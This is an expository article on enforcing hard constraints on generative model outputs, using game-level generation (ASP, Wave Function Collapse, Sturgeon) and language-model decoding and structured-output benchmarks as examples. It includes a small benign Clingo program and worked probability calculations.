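# Guaranteeing Hard Constraints on the Outputs of Learned Generative Models

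## What it means to guarantee a property of generated output

A generative model is a program that produces new outputs, such as text, images, computer code or game levels. Most generative models in wide use are learned, meaning that their behaviour comes from fitting parameters to data, whereas older generators followed rules written by people. A learned model picks up much of what its examples have in common, but it can still produce an output that breaks a condition every example met. This is often harmless, but it matters when another program reads the output and stops at the first misplaced bracket, or when the output is a path that a robot will drive along. A *hard constraint* is a condition that every output must meet, and research on hard constraints looks for ways to enforce one on a learned model without losing what the model learned.

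Game levels make a convenient test case, because they are small and a program can work out whether a player could finish them. Here is a dungeon on a grid:

```
#######
#P.#.K#
#..#..#
#.....#
#..#.D#
#######
```

The # tiles are walls and the dots are floor. P is the player, K is a key, and D is a locked door that leads out. The player moves one tile at a time, up, down, left or right, and cannot enter a wall. A level is playable if it has exactly one player, one key and one door, and the player can walk to the key and then to the door. This level is playable because of the single gap in the dividing wall.

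The dungeon is a simplified version of one from *The Legend of Zelda* that Zhang, Fontaine and colleagues used in *Video Game Level Repair via Mixed Integer Linear Programming* (2020). They trained a generative adversarial network (GAN), a learned model that imitates its training examples, on 50 human-designed levels. The GAN's levels resembled the human ones in style, but only 24.3% were playable.

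### The definition of a hard constraint

Formally, a generator is a probability distribution *a* over possible outputs, and *a*(*y*) is the probability that it produces the output *y*. For the dungeon, *y* is one way of filling the 20 tiles inside the outer wall. With five kinds of tile, there are 5²⁰ ways, or about 95 trillion. The *support* of the generator is the set of outputs with probability above zero.

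A hard constraint is a function b with two values: b(y) = 1 if y satisfies the constraint, and b(y) = 0 if it does not. Kim, Thonet and colleagues (2024), in *Guaranteed Generation from Large Language Models*, define the guarantee as a condition on the support. A generator p meets the constraint if, for every output y,

p(y) > 0 ⇒ b(y) = 1.

A single unplayable level with a probability of one in a billion is enough to violate the guarantee. The definition changes slightly for continuous outputs, because any single output then usually has probability zero. *Conditional Diffusion Guidance under Hard Constraint* (2026) requires the output to fall in the valid set "almost surely", meaning with probability one.

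A *soft constraint* is a preference that a generator may trade off against other goals. Zhang and colleagues noticed that human designers tend to put the key far from the door so that the player has to explore. A long walk from key to door would make a sensible soft constraint, because a level with a short walk is somewhat worse but still valid. Gârbacea and Mei (2022), in *Why is constrained neural language generation particularly challenging?*, make the same distinction for text. Hard-constrained generation uses a binary test to rule out infeasible sentences, while soft-constrained generation uses a graded measure, such as closeness in meaning to the words a user supplied. They warn that some soft constraints are likely to go unmet, especially when a text has to satisfy several that are largely unrelated. They also reserve the word "constraint" for something one can test on the output.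 A prompt that asks for a playable level is therefore part of the input, and the generated level still needs testing.

A low violation rate does not guarantee that every output will satisfy the constraint. If each output independently has a 1 in 10,000 chance of violating it, the chance of at least one violation in 10,000 outputs is 1 − (1 − 0.0001)^10,000, or about 63%. The rate also applies only to the kind of request used to measure it, so a user who deliberately looks for a violation may find one much faster.

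Hard constraints, as the term is used here, are sample-wise, meaning that each output must satisfy them. *Primal-Dual Flow Matching for Sample-Wise Constrained Generation* (2026) distinguishes sample-wise constraints from distributional constraints, which apply to the distribution as a whole. "Half of all levels put the key in the left half of the map" is a distributional constraint, and no single level can violate it.

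### The conditioned distribution

A guarantee by itself is easy to get. A program that prints the dungeon above every time somebody runs it will never produce an unplayable level, and nobody would want it. Kim and colleagues make the same observation about text, and so they add a second requirement: the constrained generator should distort the original one as little as possible. This leads to the *conditioned distribution*,

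g(y) = a(y) b(y) / Z, where Z = Σ a(y) b(y).

The product a(y) b(y) sets the probability of every invalid output to zero and leaves the others alone. What remains adds up to Z, the probability that the original generator produces a valid output, and dividing by Z makes the total one again. Take a generator that knows only four levels, two of them playable:

| Level | a(y) | b(y) | g(y) |
|---|---|---|---|
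| 1 | 0.40 | 0 | 0 |
| 2 | 0.30 | 1 | 0.75 |
| 3 | 0.20 | 0 | 0 |
| 4 | 0.10 | 1 | 0.25 |

Here Z is 0.40, and level 2 is still three times as likely as level 4. In general, g preserves the relative probabilities that the model learned for valid outputs. Kim and colleagues illustrate why this matters with two sentences, one saying that potatoes were first cultivated in South America and the other saying Africa. If both satisfy the constraint and the model makes the first 100 times as likely as the second, the first is also 100 times as likely under g.

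There is also a more formal argument for g. The Kullback–Leibler divergence KL(p‖a), the average of log(p(y)/a(y)) over outputs drawn from p, is a standard measure of how far a distribution p has moved from a. For any p that produces only valid outputs, Kim and colleagues show that

KL(p‖a) = KL(p‖g) − log Z.

The last term does not depend on p, and a divergence is never negative, so the left side is smallest when p equals g. In the four-level example, g has a divergence of 0.92 from the original (using natural logarithms). A generator that always returns level 2 has a divergence of 1.20, and one that always returns level 4 has a divergence of 2.30.

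How good a target g is depends on the original model, because g inherits every fault that b does not test for. Zhang and colleagues point out that a level with player, key and door side by side is technically playable, and if a GAN often generates such levels, conditioning on playability will make them more common. The formula also defines g without providing a way to sample from it, and a generator that always satisfies the constraint can still be far from g.

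### Sound and complete checkers

The function b is a mathematical ideal. A computer instead runs a *checker*, a program that takes an output and reports whether it meets the *specification*, the formal statement of the constraint. A checker is *sound* if it never passes an output that violates the specification, and *complete* if it never rejects an output that satisfies it.

A playability test for the 1983 game *Lode Runner* is a real example of incompleteness. The player collects gold and can dig through brick floors to reach it. In *Learning Local Constraints for Reinforcement-Learned Content Generators*, Bhaumik, Togelius and colleagues (2026) test whether the player can reach all the gold, but leave out digging to keep the test fast. Only 22.67% of the game's original levels pass. The test may also be unsound, because it ignores moving enemies and the possibility of getting stuck after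 collecting gold in the wrong order. Bhaumik and colleagues acknowledge this and call what they measure "perceived playability".

Software that forces language models to write JSON, a common text format for structured data, provides good evidence of unsoundness. The user supplies a schema, which lists the fields and the kinds of value that the data may contain, and the software is meant to block everything else. *JSONSchemaBench* (Geng, Cooper and colleagues, 2025) ran four such programs through an official test suite with 45 categories, roughly one for each feature of the schema language. XGrammar let through at least one invalid output in 38 of the categories, while Guidance, another of the four, did so in one. XGrammar's permissiveness had a benefit, though, as it failed to process a schema in only 3 categories, compared with 25 for Guidance.

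The guarantee depends only on soundness. A checker that rejects everything is sound, but it is useless in the same way as the program that prints one level. An incomplete checker reduces variety by rejecting valid outputs. For example, the *Lode Runner* checker would remove the levels that require digging from a generator's output.

Soundness and completeness also apply to unfinished outputs. *ChopChop* (Nagy, Zhou and colleagues, 2025) uses the terms for a checker that is given only the beginning of a program, while a model is still writing it. The checker is sound if every beginning it accepts can be extended into a valid program, and complete if it accepts every beginning that can be extended this way.

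### Local, global and undecidable constraints

How hard it is to build a good checker depends on the constraint. Some constraints are *local*, meaning that one can test them by looking at a few neighbouring tiles at a time. Wave Function Collapse, an algorithm popular with game designers, uses only local constraints. It cuts example levels into small square patterns and records which patterns may sit next to each other. Reachability is *global*. If one more wall tile fills the gap in the dungeon's dividing wall, the player can no longer get to the key or the door. Yet every two-by-two block of tiles in the broken level also occurs somewhere in the intact one, so checking such blocks can't reveal the damage. A level can also look wrong and still be playable. Bhaumik and colleagues mention a *Super Mario Bros.* level with floor tiles scattered across the sky, which is playable if a path to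 the goal exists.

A global constraint can still be quick to check. For the dungeon, a flood fill is enough. It starts at the player, marks every neighbouring tile that is not a wall, and repeats this from each newly marked tile except the door. The level passes if the marks reach both the key and the door. Each tile needs at most one visit, so the time grows in proportion to the size of the map. *PCGRLLM* (2025) uses the same technique for levels in which a locked door separates the player from a treasure chest.

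Small changes to the rules of the game make the problem much harder. *Gaming is a hard job, but someone has to do it!* (Viglietta, 2012) considers levels with one-way corridors and keys that each open any door but work only once. In one such level, each of n rooms contains two keys, every corridor between rooms has a locked door, and a row of n locked doors separates the starting room from the exit. A player who visits k rooms and returns to the start has collected 2k keys and used at least k. The player has used exactly k only if the route was a loop that never repeated a room. To have n keys left for the exit, the player therefore needs such a loop through all n rooms. Deciding whether one exists is the Hamiltonian cycle problem, which is NP-complete and has no known algorithm that stays fast as n grows. Viglietta also shows that adding pressure plates that open and close doors makes the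 problem PSPACE-hard, which most researchers believe is harder still.

Some constraints are beyond what any program can decide. *You Can't Solve These Super Mario Bros. Levels* (Demaine, Hall and colleagues, 2024) presents levels for several Mario games in which the number of enemies at one spot acts as a counter. With a few such counters, a level can imitate any computer program, and Mario can reach the goal only if that program eventually stops. Whether an arbitrary program stops is the halting problem, which Alan Turing proved undecidable in 1936. The result assumes an idealised game with room for any number of enemies and practically no time limit, so it does not apply literally to a console with finite memory. A program that tries all sequences of button presses will eventually find a winning one if the level can be finished, but it may run forever if the level cannot. A checker that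 is sound and always returns an answer must therefore reject some valid levels.

### How language models and diffusion models produce an output

A language model writes text one *token* at a time. A token is a short string of characters from a fixed vocabulary, often a fragment of a word. *Flexible and Efficient Grammar-Constrained Decoding* (2025) points out that one token may cover several symbols of a programming language or only part of one. At each step the model computes a number ℓ(v), the logit, for every token v, and the *softmax* function turns these numbers into probabilities: p(v) = exp(ℓ(v)) / Σ exp(ℓ(w)), where the sum runs over all tokens w. For example, if a model writing a dungeon row by row had only the tokens wall, floor and key, with logits 2, 1 and −1, the softmax would give them probabilities of about 71%, 26% and 3.5%. The exponential of a finite number is always positive,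 so no token gets a probability of exactly zero. The program that runs the model draws one token at random according to these probabilities, appends it to the text and feeds the longer text back in, until it draws a special token that marks the end. The probability of the whole text is the product of the probabilities of the tokens drawn at each step.

A *diffusion model* generates all parts of the output at once. *The Principles of Diffusion Models* (Lai, Song and colleagues, 2025) describes it as two opposite processes. The forward process gradually replaces a training example with noise. In the usual version, step t computes xₜ = √(1 − βₜ) xₜ₋₁ + √βₜ ε, where x₀ is the example as a list of numbers, ε is fresh Gaussian noise and βₜ is a small number fixed in advance. After enough steps, practically nothing of the example remains. A neural network learns the reverse process, which removes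 a little of the noise at each step. To generate a new output, one starts from pure noise and applies the network repeatedly. For the dungeon, the list could hold one number for each kind of tile at each position, and the largest number at a position would determine its tile. According to *Memorization and Generalization in Generative Models* (2026), diffusion underlies the best current generators of images, audio and video.

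### Four points at which a constraint can act

A designer can apply a constraint through written rules, in training, during generation or after generation. With written rules, a solver constructs only outputs that obey them. *Level Generation with Constrained Expressive Range* (2025) uses such a generator, Sturgeon, whose levels meet the written constraints exactly. Training can take account of a constraint through a change to the model's objective or architecture. During generation, a program can block or redirect single steps. For language models this means giving disallowed tokens zero probability, which, as *Decode-Time Grammars* (2026) notes, neither prompting nor fine-tuning does. After generation, a checker can reject a finished level, or a second program can repair it. According to *Primal-Dual Flow Matching*, building a constraint into a learned model usually takes extra training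 but leaves generation about as fast as before, while intervening during generation works with an existing model but usually requires more computation for each output.

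## Generators built from hand-written rules

A designer describes the valid outputs in a formal language, and a *constraint solver*, a general-purpose search program, looks for outputs that fit the description. Smith and Mateas (2011) proposed making game content this way in *Answer Set Programming for Procedural Content Generation*. They argued that it is easier to start from a large space of levels and remove the bad ones, one describable flaw at a time, than to guess a procedure that avoids every flaw.

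### Answer set programming

Answer set programming (ASP) is a form of logic programming. A program consists of facts and rules, and a solver returns *answer sets*, which are collections of facts consistent with the whole program. The program below generates playable versions of the dungeon, one level per answer set. It uses the syntax of Clingo, a free ASP solver.

```
cell(1..5, 1..4).
kind(wall; floor; player; key; door).
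unique(player; key; door).

{ tile(X,Y,K) : kind(K) } = 1 :- cell(X,Y).
:- unique(K), { tile(X,Y,K) : cell(X,Y) } != 1.

reach(X,Y) :- tile(X,Y,player).
reach(V,W) :- reach(X,Y), not tile(X,Y,door),
              cell(V,W), not tile(V,W,wall),
              |X-V| + |Y-W| = 1.
:- unique(K), tile(X,Y,K), not reach(X,Y).
```

The first three lines list the cells inside the outer wall, the kinds of tile, and the kinds that must occur exactly once. The sign `:-` means "if". The fourth line is a *choice rule*, which makes the solver choose exactly one kind of tile for (X,Y) if (X,Y) is a cell. These four lines allow all 95 trillion fillings. The next line is an *integrity constraint*, which has nothing to the left of the "if". The solver rejects every level that matches the right-hand side, which here means any level that doesn't have exactly one player, one key and one door.

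The two `reach` rules define the flood fill recursively, with one rule for the player's tile and one for the step to a neighbouring tile. The last line rejects any level whose key or door is out of reach.

Every answer set is a playable level, because it must satisfy all the constraints and can contain a `reach` fact only if the rules derive it step by step from the player's position. This prevents circular reasoning. Two neighbouring floor tiles in a sealed room would each be reachable if the other were, but neither counts because no derivation leads to them from the player. The `reach` facts therefore match the tiles that a flood fill would mark, so a level that fails the flood fill also violates the last constraint. Conversely, every playable level is an answer set. If no level satisfies the rules, the solver reports that, and Smith and Mateas used this to prove that mazes of one type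 cannot have a shortest solution above a certain length.

To find an answer, Clingo first replaces the variables in each rule with every possible combination of values. It then makes one choice at a time, works out the consequences, and goes back when it reaches a conflict. This lets it reject unfinished levels. Suppose it has put the player in the top left corner and walls on the two free neighbouring tiles. The player can't reach anything, so Clingo can discard all 5¹⁷ (about 763 billion) ways of filling the other 17 tiles without building any of them. ASP solvers can also record the combination of choices that caused a conflict and avoid repeating it.

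Nelson and Smith (2016), in *ASP with applications to mazes and levels*, use a different technique for a dungeon where the player must carry a gem to an altar before leaving. Their program makes the solver choose a route through the level along with the level itself. A completed route proves that the level has a solution but proves nothing about the other solutions, and in many of the levels the gem and the altar were only a small detour on the way to the exit. Nelson and Smith wanted the player to have to spend some time at each stage. That constraint has to hold for all possible routes, because if only the chosen route had to be long, the solver could pick a winding route through a level that also has a short one. Enforcing it takes an extension of ASP and a solver for problems that most researchers believe are harder than NP-complete ones.

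### Wave Function Collapse

Game developers often prefer Wave Function Collapse, which Maxim Gumin released in 2016, because it takes its constraints from an example image and nobody has to write logic. After cutting the example into patterns, it works as follows:

1. Every cell of the output starts with all patterns possible.
2. The algorithm picks the undecided cell with the lowest *entropy*. Entropy measures how open the choice at a cell still is, given the remaining patterns and how common each one is in the example.
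3. It draws one of the remaining patterns for that cell at random, favouring those that are common in the example.
4. It removes every pattern that no longer fits from the neighbouring cells, then from their neighbours, and so on until nothing changes. This step is called *propagation*.
5. It returns to step 2 until every cell has one pattern left. If a cell has no patterns left, the algorithm has reached a *contradiction*, and Gumin's version starts again from an empty grid.

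Suppose the example is the intact dungeon and the patterns are single tiles. If the algorithm places a key, the cells to the left of it and below it must be floor, because only floor appears in those positions in the example. The cell two below the key then can't hold a player or a key, since neither appears directly under a floor tile in the example.

Karth and Smith (2017), in *WaveFunctionCollapse is Constraint Solving in the Wild*, recognised the procedure as constraint solving. Each cell is a variable, its patterns are the possible values, and both propagation and choosing the most restricted cell are textbook techniques. They restated the problem in ASP with a choice rule that gives each cell exactly one pattern and an integrity constraint that forbids neighbouring patterns that do not match.

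With these two rules, Clingo generated images of 48 by 48 cells from three of Gumin's examples without undoing a choice. It made an average of between 325 and 433 choices per image, and propagation settled the rest of the 2,304 cells. The result still held when Karth and Smith turned off Clingo's search heuristics, so that it filled the grid in reading order. But when it picked cells in random order, it never finished within the one-minute limit. Propagation therefore seems to matter more than entropy, as long as the algorithm keeps working next to cells it has already filled.

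Wave Function Collapse guarantees only that its adjacency rules hold. Given two-by-two patterns from the intact dungeon, it could still produce the broken one in which a wall fills the gap, or a dungeon with three keys or none. The developers of *Caves of Qud*, a commercial game that uses the algorithm, add doorways and connections afterwards to make sure the parts of a level are joined.

Adding a global constraint can make the search harder. Karth and Smith required every pattern in the example to appear at least once in the output. For two of the examples this made little difference. For the third, a city skyline, Clingo ran into hundreds of conflicts. It still found a solution quickly when it could backtrack, but found none within the one-minute limit when it had to restart after every conflict, as Gumin's version does.

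### Why restarts fail on large grids

Even without a global constraint, restarting stops working as the grid grows. A larger grid has more places where a contradiction can occur, and a single contradiction makes the whole attempt fail. Merrell (2021) measured this on several textures in *Comparing Model Synthesis and Wave Function Collapse*. For the Rooms texture, 45.9% of attempts succeeded on a grid of 100 by 100 cells, but only 1.8% on a grid of 200 by 200. If the four 100 by 100 quarters of the larger grid succeeded independently, the rate would be 0.459⁴, or about 4.4%. For the Castle texture, none of 10,000 attempts succeeded even at the smaller size.

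Merrell invented model synthesis, an earlier and nearly identical algorithm, and so has a stake in the comparison. Model synthesis fills cells in reading order and can rebuild a large grid one block at a time. It took about 4 seconds to make the larger Rooms texture, while Wave Function Collapse took about 201 seconds, including failed attempts. Merrell attributes most of the difference in these tests to the order of the cells. The algorithm never fails for some sets of tiles, but Merrell proved that the problem is NP-hard for others, so no cell order is likely to make it fast in general.

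Backtracking avoids throwing away the whole grid, but it can stall. If an early choice has made one region impossible, the algorithm may keep trying variations of that region without returning to that choice. *Model Synthesis and Modifying in Blocks* (2021) describes a test on a deliberately difficult set of three-dimensional tiles, with an output of 30 by 30 by 10 cells. Restarts and backtracking both failed to complete it. Solving overlapping blocks one after another succeeded because a contradiction then meant losing only one block, but the method needed careful tuning and a known valid arrangement to start from. Zzyzek (2025) proposes a related block-by-block method that needs fewer assumptions and randomly erodes the edges of finished regions when it gets stuck.

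Backtracking is also awkward in a world that grows during play. According to *Extend Wave Function Collapse to Large-Scale Content Generation* (2023), the developer of the experimental game *Infinite City* found that backtracking could force the program to regenerate existing parts of the city.

### Sturgeon: example patterns with guaranteed paths

Wave Function Collapse makes it easy to get rules from examples, and ASP can express reachability. *Sturgeon* (Cooper, 2022) combines these abilities in a level generator and tests it on seven games, including *Super Mario Bros.* and *The Legend of Zelda*. The generator extracts patterns from example levels and turns them into constraints on true-or-false variables, such as "this cell contains a wall". A designer can add other constraints, such as exactly three question blocks. The generator then passes all the constraints to standard solvers.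 It also has a soft constraint that keeps the number of each kind of tile within 50% of the proportion in the example.

For reachability, Sturgeon represents the level as a graph, with a node for each cell and an arrow for each move the player might make. An arrow for a jump, for instance, is usable only if there is solid ground under the starting point and open space along the arc. The solver has to select a set of usable arrows and the nodes they connect, subject to these conditions:

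- The solver must select the start and the goal.
- No selected arrow leads into the start or out of the goal.
- Each node has at most one selected arrow in and one out.
- Every selected node except the start has a selected arrow in.

These conditions guarantee a path from the start to the goal. A trail that follows the selected arrows backwards from the goal can never revisit a node, because that would require a second arrow out of the node or an arrow out of the goal, and the conditions allow neither. The level is finite, so the trail must end, and it can only end at the start, which is the only selected node that may lack an arrow in. The solver sometimes selects extra loops separate from this path, which also satisfy the conditions and do no harm.

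This version of Sturgeon guarantees a path from one start to one goal. Cooper left locks and keys to future work, so Sturgeon doesn't guarantee that the player of a Zelda level can pick up a key along the way. A later version, Sturgeon-MKIII, generates a complete playthrough together with the level, much as Nelson and Smith's program does for the gem and the altar.

A designer can also treat the global property as a goal and leave only adjacency as a hard constraint. In *A Markovian Framing of WaveFunctionCollapse for Procedurally Generating Aesthetically Complex Environments* (Yiu, Lu and colleagues, 2025), Wave Function Collapse blocked tiles that did not fit, while an evolutionary algorithm learned which of the remaining tiles to choose. The goal was a map whose longest shortest path had a given length. For lengths up to 40, this method succeeded in all or nearly all runs, while evolutionary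 algorithms that also had to learn the adjacency rules sometimes failed. Path length was not a hard constraint, so the method could not guarantee it, and it became unreliable for the hardest goals.

### The cost of writing rules and solving them

The person writing the rules needs to understand both the game and the language. The programs can be short. Smith and Mateas needed 49 lines for a generator of *chromatic mazes*, grids of coloured tiles in which the player may only step to the same colour or a neighbouring one on a colour wheel. Smith, who already had experience with ASP, wrote that generator and two others in under four hours. Much of the work is finding out which rules are missing. An early version of their generator for small arcade games produced games where the player had to escape from a completely walled-in area. When the designer sees such a game, they describe the flaw and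 add a constraint to rule it out.

Solving time is harder to predict. In the worst case, it grows exponentially with the size of the program once the solver has filled in its variables. According to Smith and Mateas, the hardest problems tend to be those with only one answer in a huge space, while most realistic content problems have many answers and are easy. Their generator produced 10,000 different six-by-six mazes in one second. On a 21-by-21 grid, however, they asked for mazes with ever longer solutions, and after two hours the best maze took 114 steps to solve. The evolutionary algorithm they were reimplementing had found one that took 292 steps, though they do not know how long it ran.

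A time limit also makes failures harder to interpret. Cooper used Sturgeon to search for 36 *Super Mario Bros.* levels, each with a different combination of gaps and solid tiles, and allowed ten minutes per level. Sturgeon found 19. Seven searches ran out of time, so they do not show whether such levels exist.

Smith, Andersen and colleagues (2012) built puzzle generators for *Refraction*, a game that teaches fractions with laser beams. In *A Case Study of Expressively Constrainable Level Design Automation Tools*, they call these generators "correct by design" because they always produce a valid puzzle if one exists and the search finishes. A game that generates levels while the player waits would need a fallback, such as a stored level, in case the search takes too long.

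### Valid levels can still be unrepresentative or dull

Hand-written rules determine which outputs a generator can produce, but not how likely each one is. Unlike a learned model, a solver has no distribution of its own to restrict to valid outputs. Most solvers return the first solution they find, which depends on the order in which they try the options.

In *You-Only-Randomize-Once*, Katz, Bateni and Smith (2024) used an example image with 46 black cells and 3 white ones, whose adjacency rules allowed any arrangement of the two colours. With the default order, the solver tried black first everywhere and returned a completely black image, which was valid. On a map from *The Legend of Zelda*, the default order produced a valid map that was mostly rock, and a second run gave exactly the same map.

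Their remedy is to shuffle the options before the solver starts. For each cell, every tile i gets a score

sᵢ = log wᵢ − log(−log uᵢ),

where wᵢ is the frequency of the tile in the example and uᵢ is a fresh random number between 0 and 1. The tile with the highest score is tile i with probability wᵢ / Σ wⱼ. Sorting all tiles by score is equivalent to drawing them one by one without replacement, with these frequencies as weights. The solver then works through the cells and takes the highest-ranked tile that the constraints allow. In the black-and-white test, the share of each colour came within 1% of the example.

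The scores reflect the frequency of single tiles, not shapes, so the output contained only one L like the one formed by the three white cells in the example. Katz and colleagues got closer to the example on the Zelda map by ranking whole neighbourhoods of tiles. They also had to switch off the heuristics that normally speed up a solver, because these change the order of the options, and they never got Clasp, the solver inside Clingo, to follow their order on that map. Other tools sample almost evenly from all solutions, but an even sample would not resemble the example either.

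Hand-written rules cannot guarantee a quality that nobody has written down. Smith and Mateas mention beauty and fun as properties that often only a person can judge, and suggest listing concrete failures instead, such as the ways a maze can look too easy. Smith, Andersen and colleagues went quite far in formalizing such qualities for *Refraction*. Designers could require symmetry, visual balance or a certain spacing between pieces, but someone first had to notice each quality and describe it formally.

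### Rules taken from examples or drafted by a model

Extracting rules from examples saves much of the work of writing them by hand, but the guarantee then depends on how well the rules capture what the designer wanted. They can be too strict or too loose. When Cooper extracted patterns of two whole rows from a *Kid Icarus* level, the new levels varied little because Sturgeon reproduced the original's beginning and end almost exactly. With smaller patterns, levels for *Super Mario Land* contained unfinished pyramids, because every group of tiles that Sturgeon checked was acceptable but no rule required a complete pyramid.

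Karth and Smith (2021) describe the WaveFunctionCollapse algorithm as a combination of machine learning and constraint solving, trained on a single small image. The solver strictly enforces the patterns learned from that image, including accidental ones. If the only key in the image happens to have a wall above it, every key in the output will have one too.

A language model can also draft the rules, but the guarantee then covers only the rules as written. In the ASP program above, a model could easily leave out the condition `not tile(X,Y,door)`. The program would still run, and most of its levels would look fine. But the reachability rule would treat the locked door as passable, so Clingo could return a level in which the key lies behind the door it is supposed to open.

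## Why training alone gives no guarantee

The solvers described above never return a level that breaks a written rule. No amount of training on valid examples can give the same guarantee for a language model that samples from its full softmax, because the softmax formula gives every token a probability above zero.

### Fine-tuning cannot reach zero

Kim and colleagues illustrate the problem with the simple constraint that a text must not contain the token "bad". Someone could generate many texts, delete those that contain the token, and *fine-tune* the model on the rest, which means continuing its training on them. The token would become rarer but would not disappear, because a softmax never outputs exactly zero. Fine-tuning only changes one finite logit into another, so every text that was possible before is still possible afterwards. Kim and colleagues note that the same holds for PPO and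 DPO, two widely used methods for training a model on feedback.

The probability can still become very small. Let d be the amount by which the logarithm of the summed exponentials of all the other logits exceeds the logit of "bad". The probability of "bad" is then 1 / (1 + exp(d)), which is about 1 in 1,100 for d = 7, 1 in 1.2 million for d = 14 and 1 in 1.3 billion for d = 21. But training lowers the logit of "bad" more slowly as d grows. The usual objective raises the log-probability of whichever token comes next in the training text, and its gradient with respect to the logit of any other token is equal in magnitude to that token's current probability. Once the probability of "bad" is down to one in a million, the gradient from each example is about a million times smaller than when the token was nearly certain. Kim and colleagues expect that even a large reduction would take a huge dataset,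 because the selected texts never contain the mistake the model should avoid.

### Greedy and truncated sampling

Many programs don't sample from the full softmax. *Greedy decoding* always takes the most likely token. *Top-k sampling* keeps only the k most likely tokens, and *nucleus sampling* keeps the smallest set of top tokens whose probabilities add up to at least some chosen share, such as 95%. All three methods give every other token a probability of exactly zero, so the argument above doesn't apply to these methods. Rounding can also produce a zero, but in ordinary 32-bit arithmetic this happens only when a token's logit is more than about 100 below the highest one.

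These zeros depend on how likely a token is, not on whether it is valid. In the earlier dungeon example, the key was the least likely of three tokens, so top-k sampling with k = 2 would remove it. If the ranking were the same at every position, the generator could never place a key, and every level would be unplayable. In another dungeon, the wall tile that closes the only gap might be the most likely token, so all three methods would keep it. To prove that truncation removes every invalid output, one would have to know how the model ranks its tokens after every partial output it can produce.

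Models still violate constraints under greedy decoding, a common setting in tests. In *The Structured Output Benchmark*, Singh, Khurdula and colleagues (2026) gave 21 models 5,000 questions about short texts, with a JSON schema in the prompt and no other enforcement. The best model, GPT-5.4, complied with the schema in 99.97% of cases, and the median compliance rate was 97.5%. Greedy decoding produces essentially one output per prompt, so a prompt that leads to a violation will tend to do so every time.

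### A limit for models that can produce zeros

Kim and colleagues prove that even a model that could assign zero probability wherever needed could not always match the conditioned distribution g, which is the original model restricted to valid outputs. Their Theorem 1 concerns *autoregressive* models, which write one token at a time, and requires everything to run in *polynomial time*, meaning that the computing time grows no faster than some fixed power of the text's length. Standard language models meet this requirement.

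The theorem rests on the conjecture P ≠ NP, which most researchers believe. It implies that for some problems a proposed solution is quick to check, yet no fast method can always tell whether a solution exists. If the conjecture is true, there are a polynomial-time autoregressive model a and a polynomial-time constraint b whose conditioned distribution g no polynomial-time autoregressive model can match. The proof goes as follows:

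1. Let a write a logical formula, then a # sign, then a value of 0 or 1 for each variable in the formula. It gives every such text a positive probability, whether or not the values make the formula true.
2. Let b accept a text only if the values make the formula true. A program can check this quickly by substituting them.
3. The support of g then consists of all formulas that have a solution, each followed by one of its solutions.
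4. Suppose a fast autoregressive model a′ had the same support. To find out whether a formula has a solution, one could feed the formula and the # sign to a′ and multiply the probabilities of the symbols. The product would be positive if a solution exists and zero otherwise.
5. That would be a fast method for an NP-complete problem, which cannot exist if P ≠ NP.

Kim and colleagues give the formula "(x₁ or not x₂ or x₃) and (not x₁ or not x₃)" as an example. Setting x₁, x₂, x₃ to 1, 1, 0 makes it true, while 0, 1, 0 makes the first bracket false. Checking either set of values is easy, but a′ has to generate the formula first, and it must never generate one that has no solution.

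The same proof works for other NP-complete problems. For example, the text could describe one of Viglietta's levels with single-use keys, followed by a list of moves that finishes it. A program can check the moves quickly by replaying them, but a model that writes the level first would have to avoid every unsolvable level before writing any moves. Since the proof doesn't use the softmax, it also applies to models that can block tokens completely.

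The theorem shows only that a difficult pair of model and constraint exists, and many pairs are easier. If the original model is an *n-gram* model, which predicts each word from only the last few, one can construct a new model that avoids or includes a given word and matches g exactly. For a neural language model, a constraint that fixes only the opening words is just as easy, because the program can supply those words and have the model generate the rest. The theorem also does not rule out close approximations.

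A model can always satisfy a hard constraint if it is allowed to distort the distribution of its outputs. For example, a program can guarantee that a 30-token text contains the word "amazing" by forcing the word into the last position whenever it has not appeared earlier. Every text then satisfies the constraint, but far too many end in "amazing". Kim and colleagues conclude that guaranteeing the constraint with little distortion requires a sampling procedure on top of the trained model.

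### What a clean test can establish

A model might produce only valid outputs without anyone being able to tell. *Query Feedback and Teaching for Stable and Certifiable Language Generation* (2026) discusses a theoretical result of this kind by Kleinberg and Mullainathan. A learner receives one valid string after another from an unknown language, which belongs to a known, countable collection of languages. With a suitable method, the learner will generate only valid strings after some finite time. But that time depends on the unknown language and the order of the examples, so the learner can never confirm that it has reached that point.

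Testing can put an upper limit on the violation rate. If each output independently violates the constraint with probability p, the chance that n outputs in a row are all valid is (1 − p)ⁿ. Setting this equal to 0.05 gives p ≈ 3/n, because the natural logarithm of 0.05 is about −3. After n samples without a violation, we can therefore be 95% confident that the rate is below about 3/n. For 10,000 samples the limit is 0.03%, which still allows about 300 violations in a million outputs. Lowering the limit to one in a billion would take about three billion samples without a violation.

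The limit applies only to inputs drawn in the same way as those in the test. In Singh and colleagues' results, GPT-5.4 complied with the schema on 99.97% of short texts, which would suggest a failure rate well below 0.2%. On 115 meeting transcripts, with the schema again in the prompt, it complied in only 86.9% of cases. The transcripts were longer, and nearly all of their schemas were in the benchmark's most complex category. A company that tested its software on short documents and later used it on meeting transcripts would have had no valid estimate of its failure rate.

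Constraints are harder to guarantee when an adversary chooses inputs to cause violations. Gray Swan's *Frontier Hazard Tracker*, a public record of safety tests by an AI security company, includes a competition from November 2026 in which people tried to get 24 models to misbehave. Attempts succeeded 0.3% of the time against the most resistant model, GPT-6.1 Terra, and 11.4% of the time against the least resistant. If attempts were independent, 1,000 of them against the most resistant model would have a 95% chance of producing at least one success. Attackers can also learn from failures and share what works, so the average over all participants may understate what a skilled attacker can do.

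### Measured violation rates

Output formats provide some of the clearest measurements of constraint violations because a program can check them exactly. In *Why Does Structured Output Fail?*, Verma (2026) tested nine models from OpenAI and Anthropic in August 2026. The prompt contained the schema, and a program checked each output and prompted the model again if it failed. Over 3,997 attempts, the failure rate ranged from 3.5% for GPT-5.6 Sol to 66.1% for Claude Haiku 4.5.

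Haiku had the highest figure because it wrapped its JSON in a code fence, a pair of markers that chat programs use to display code, in all 475 of its first attempts. A strict parser rejects these markers, though a few lines of code can remove them. Even after allowing for this, 44.2% of Haiku's attempts were invalid, mostly because a piece of text exceeded its maximum length. Other failures were more understandable. One rule required an identifier to start with a letter, but a GPT-5.6 model returned `888_7th_avenue` as the identifier for a street address. A name such as `building_888_7th_avenue` would have been valid, but nothing in the task suggested it.

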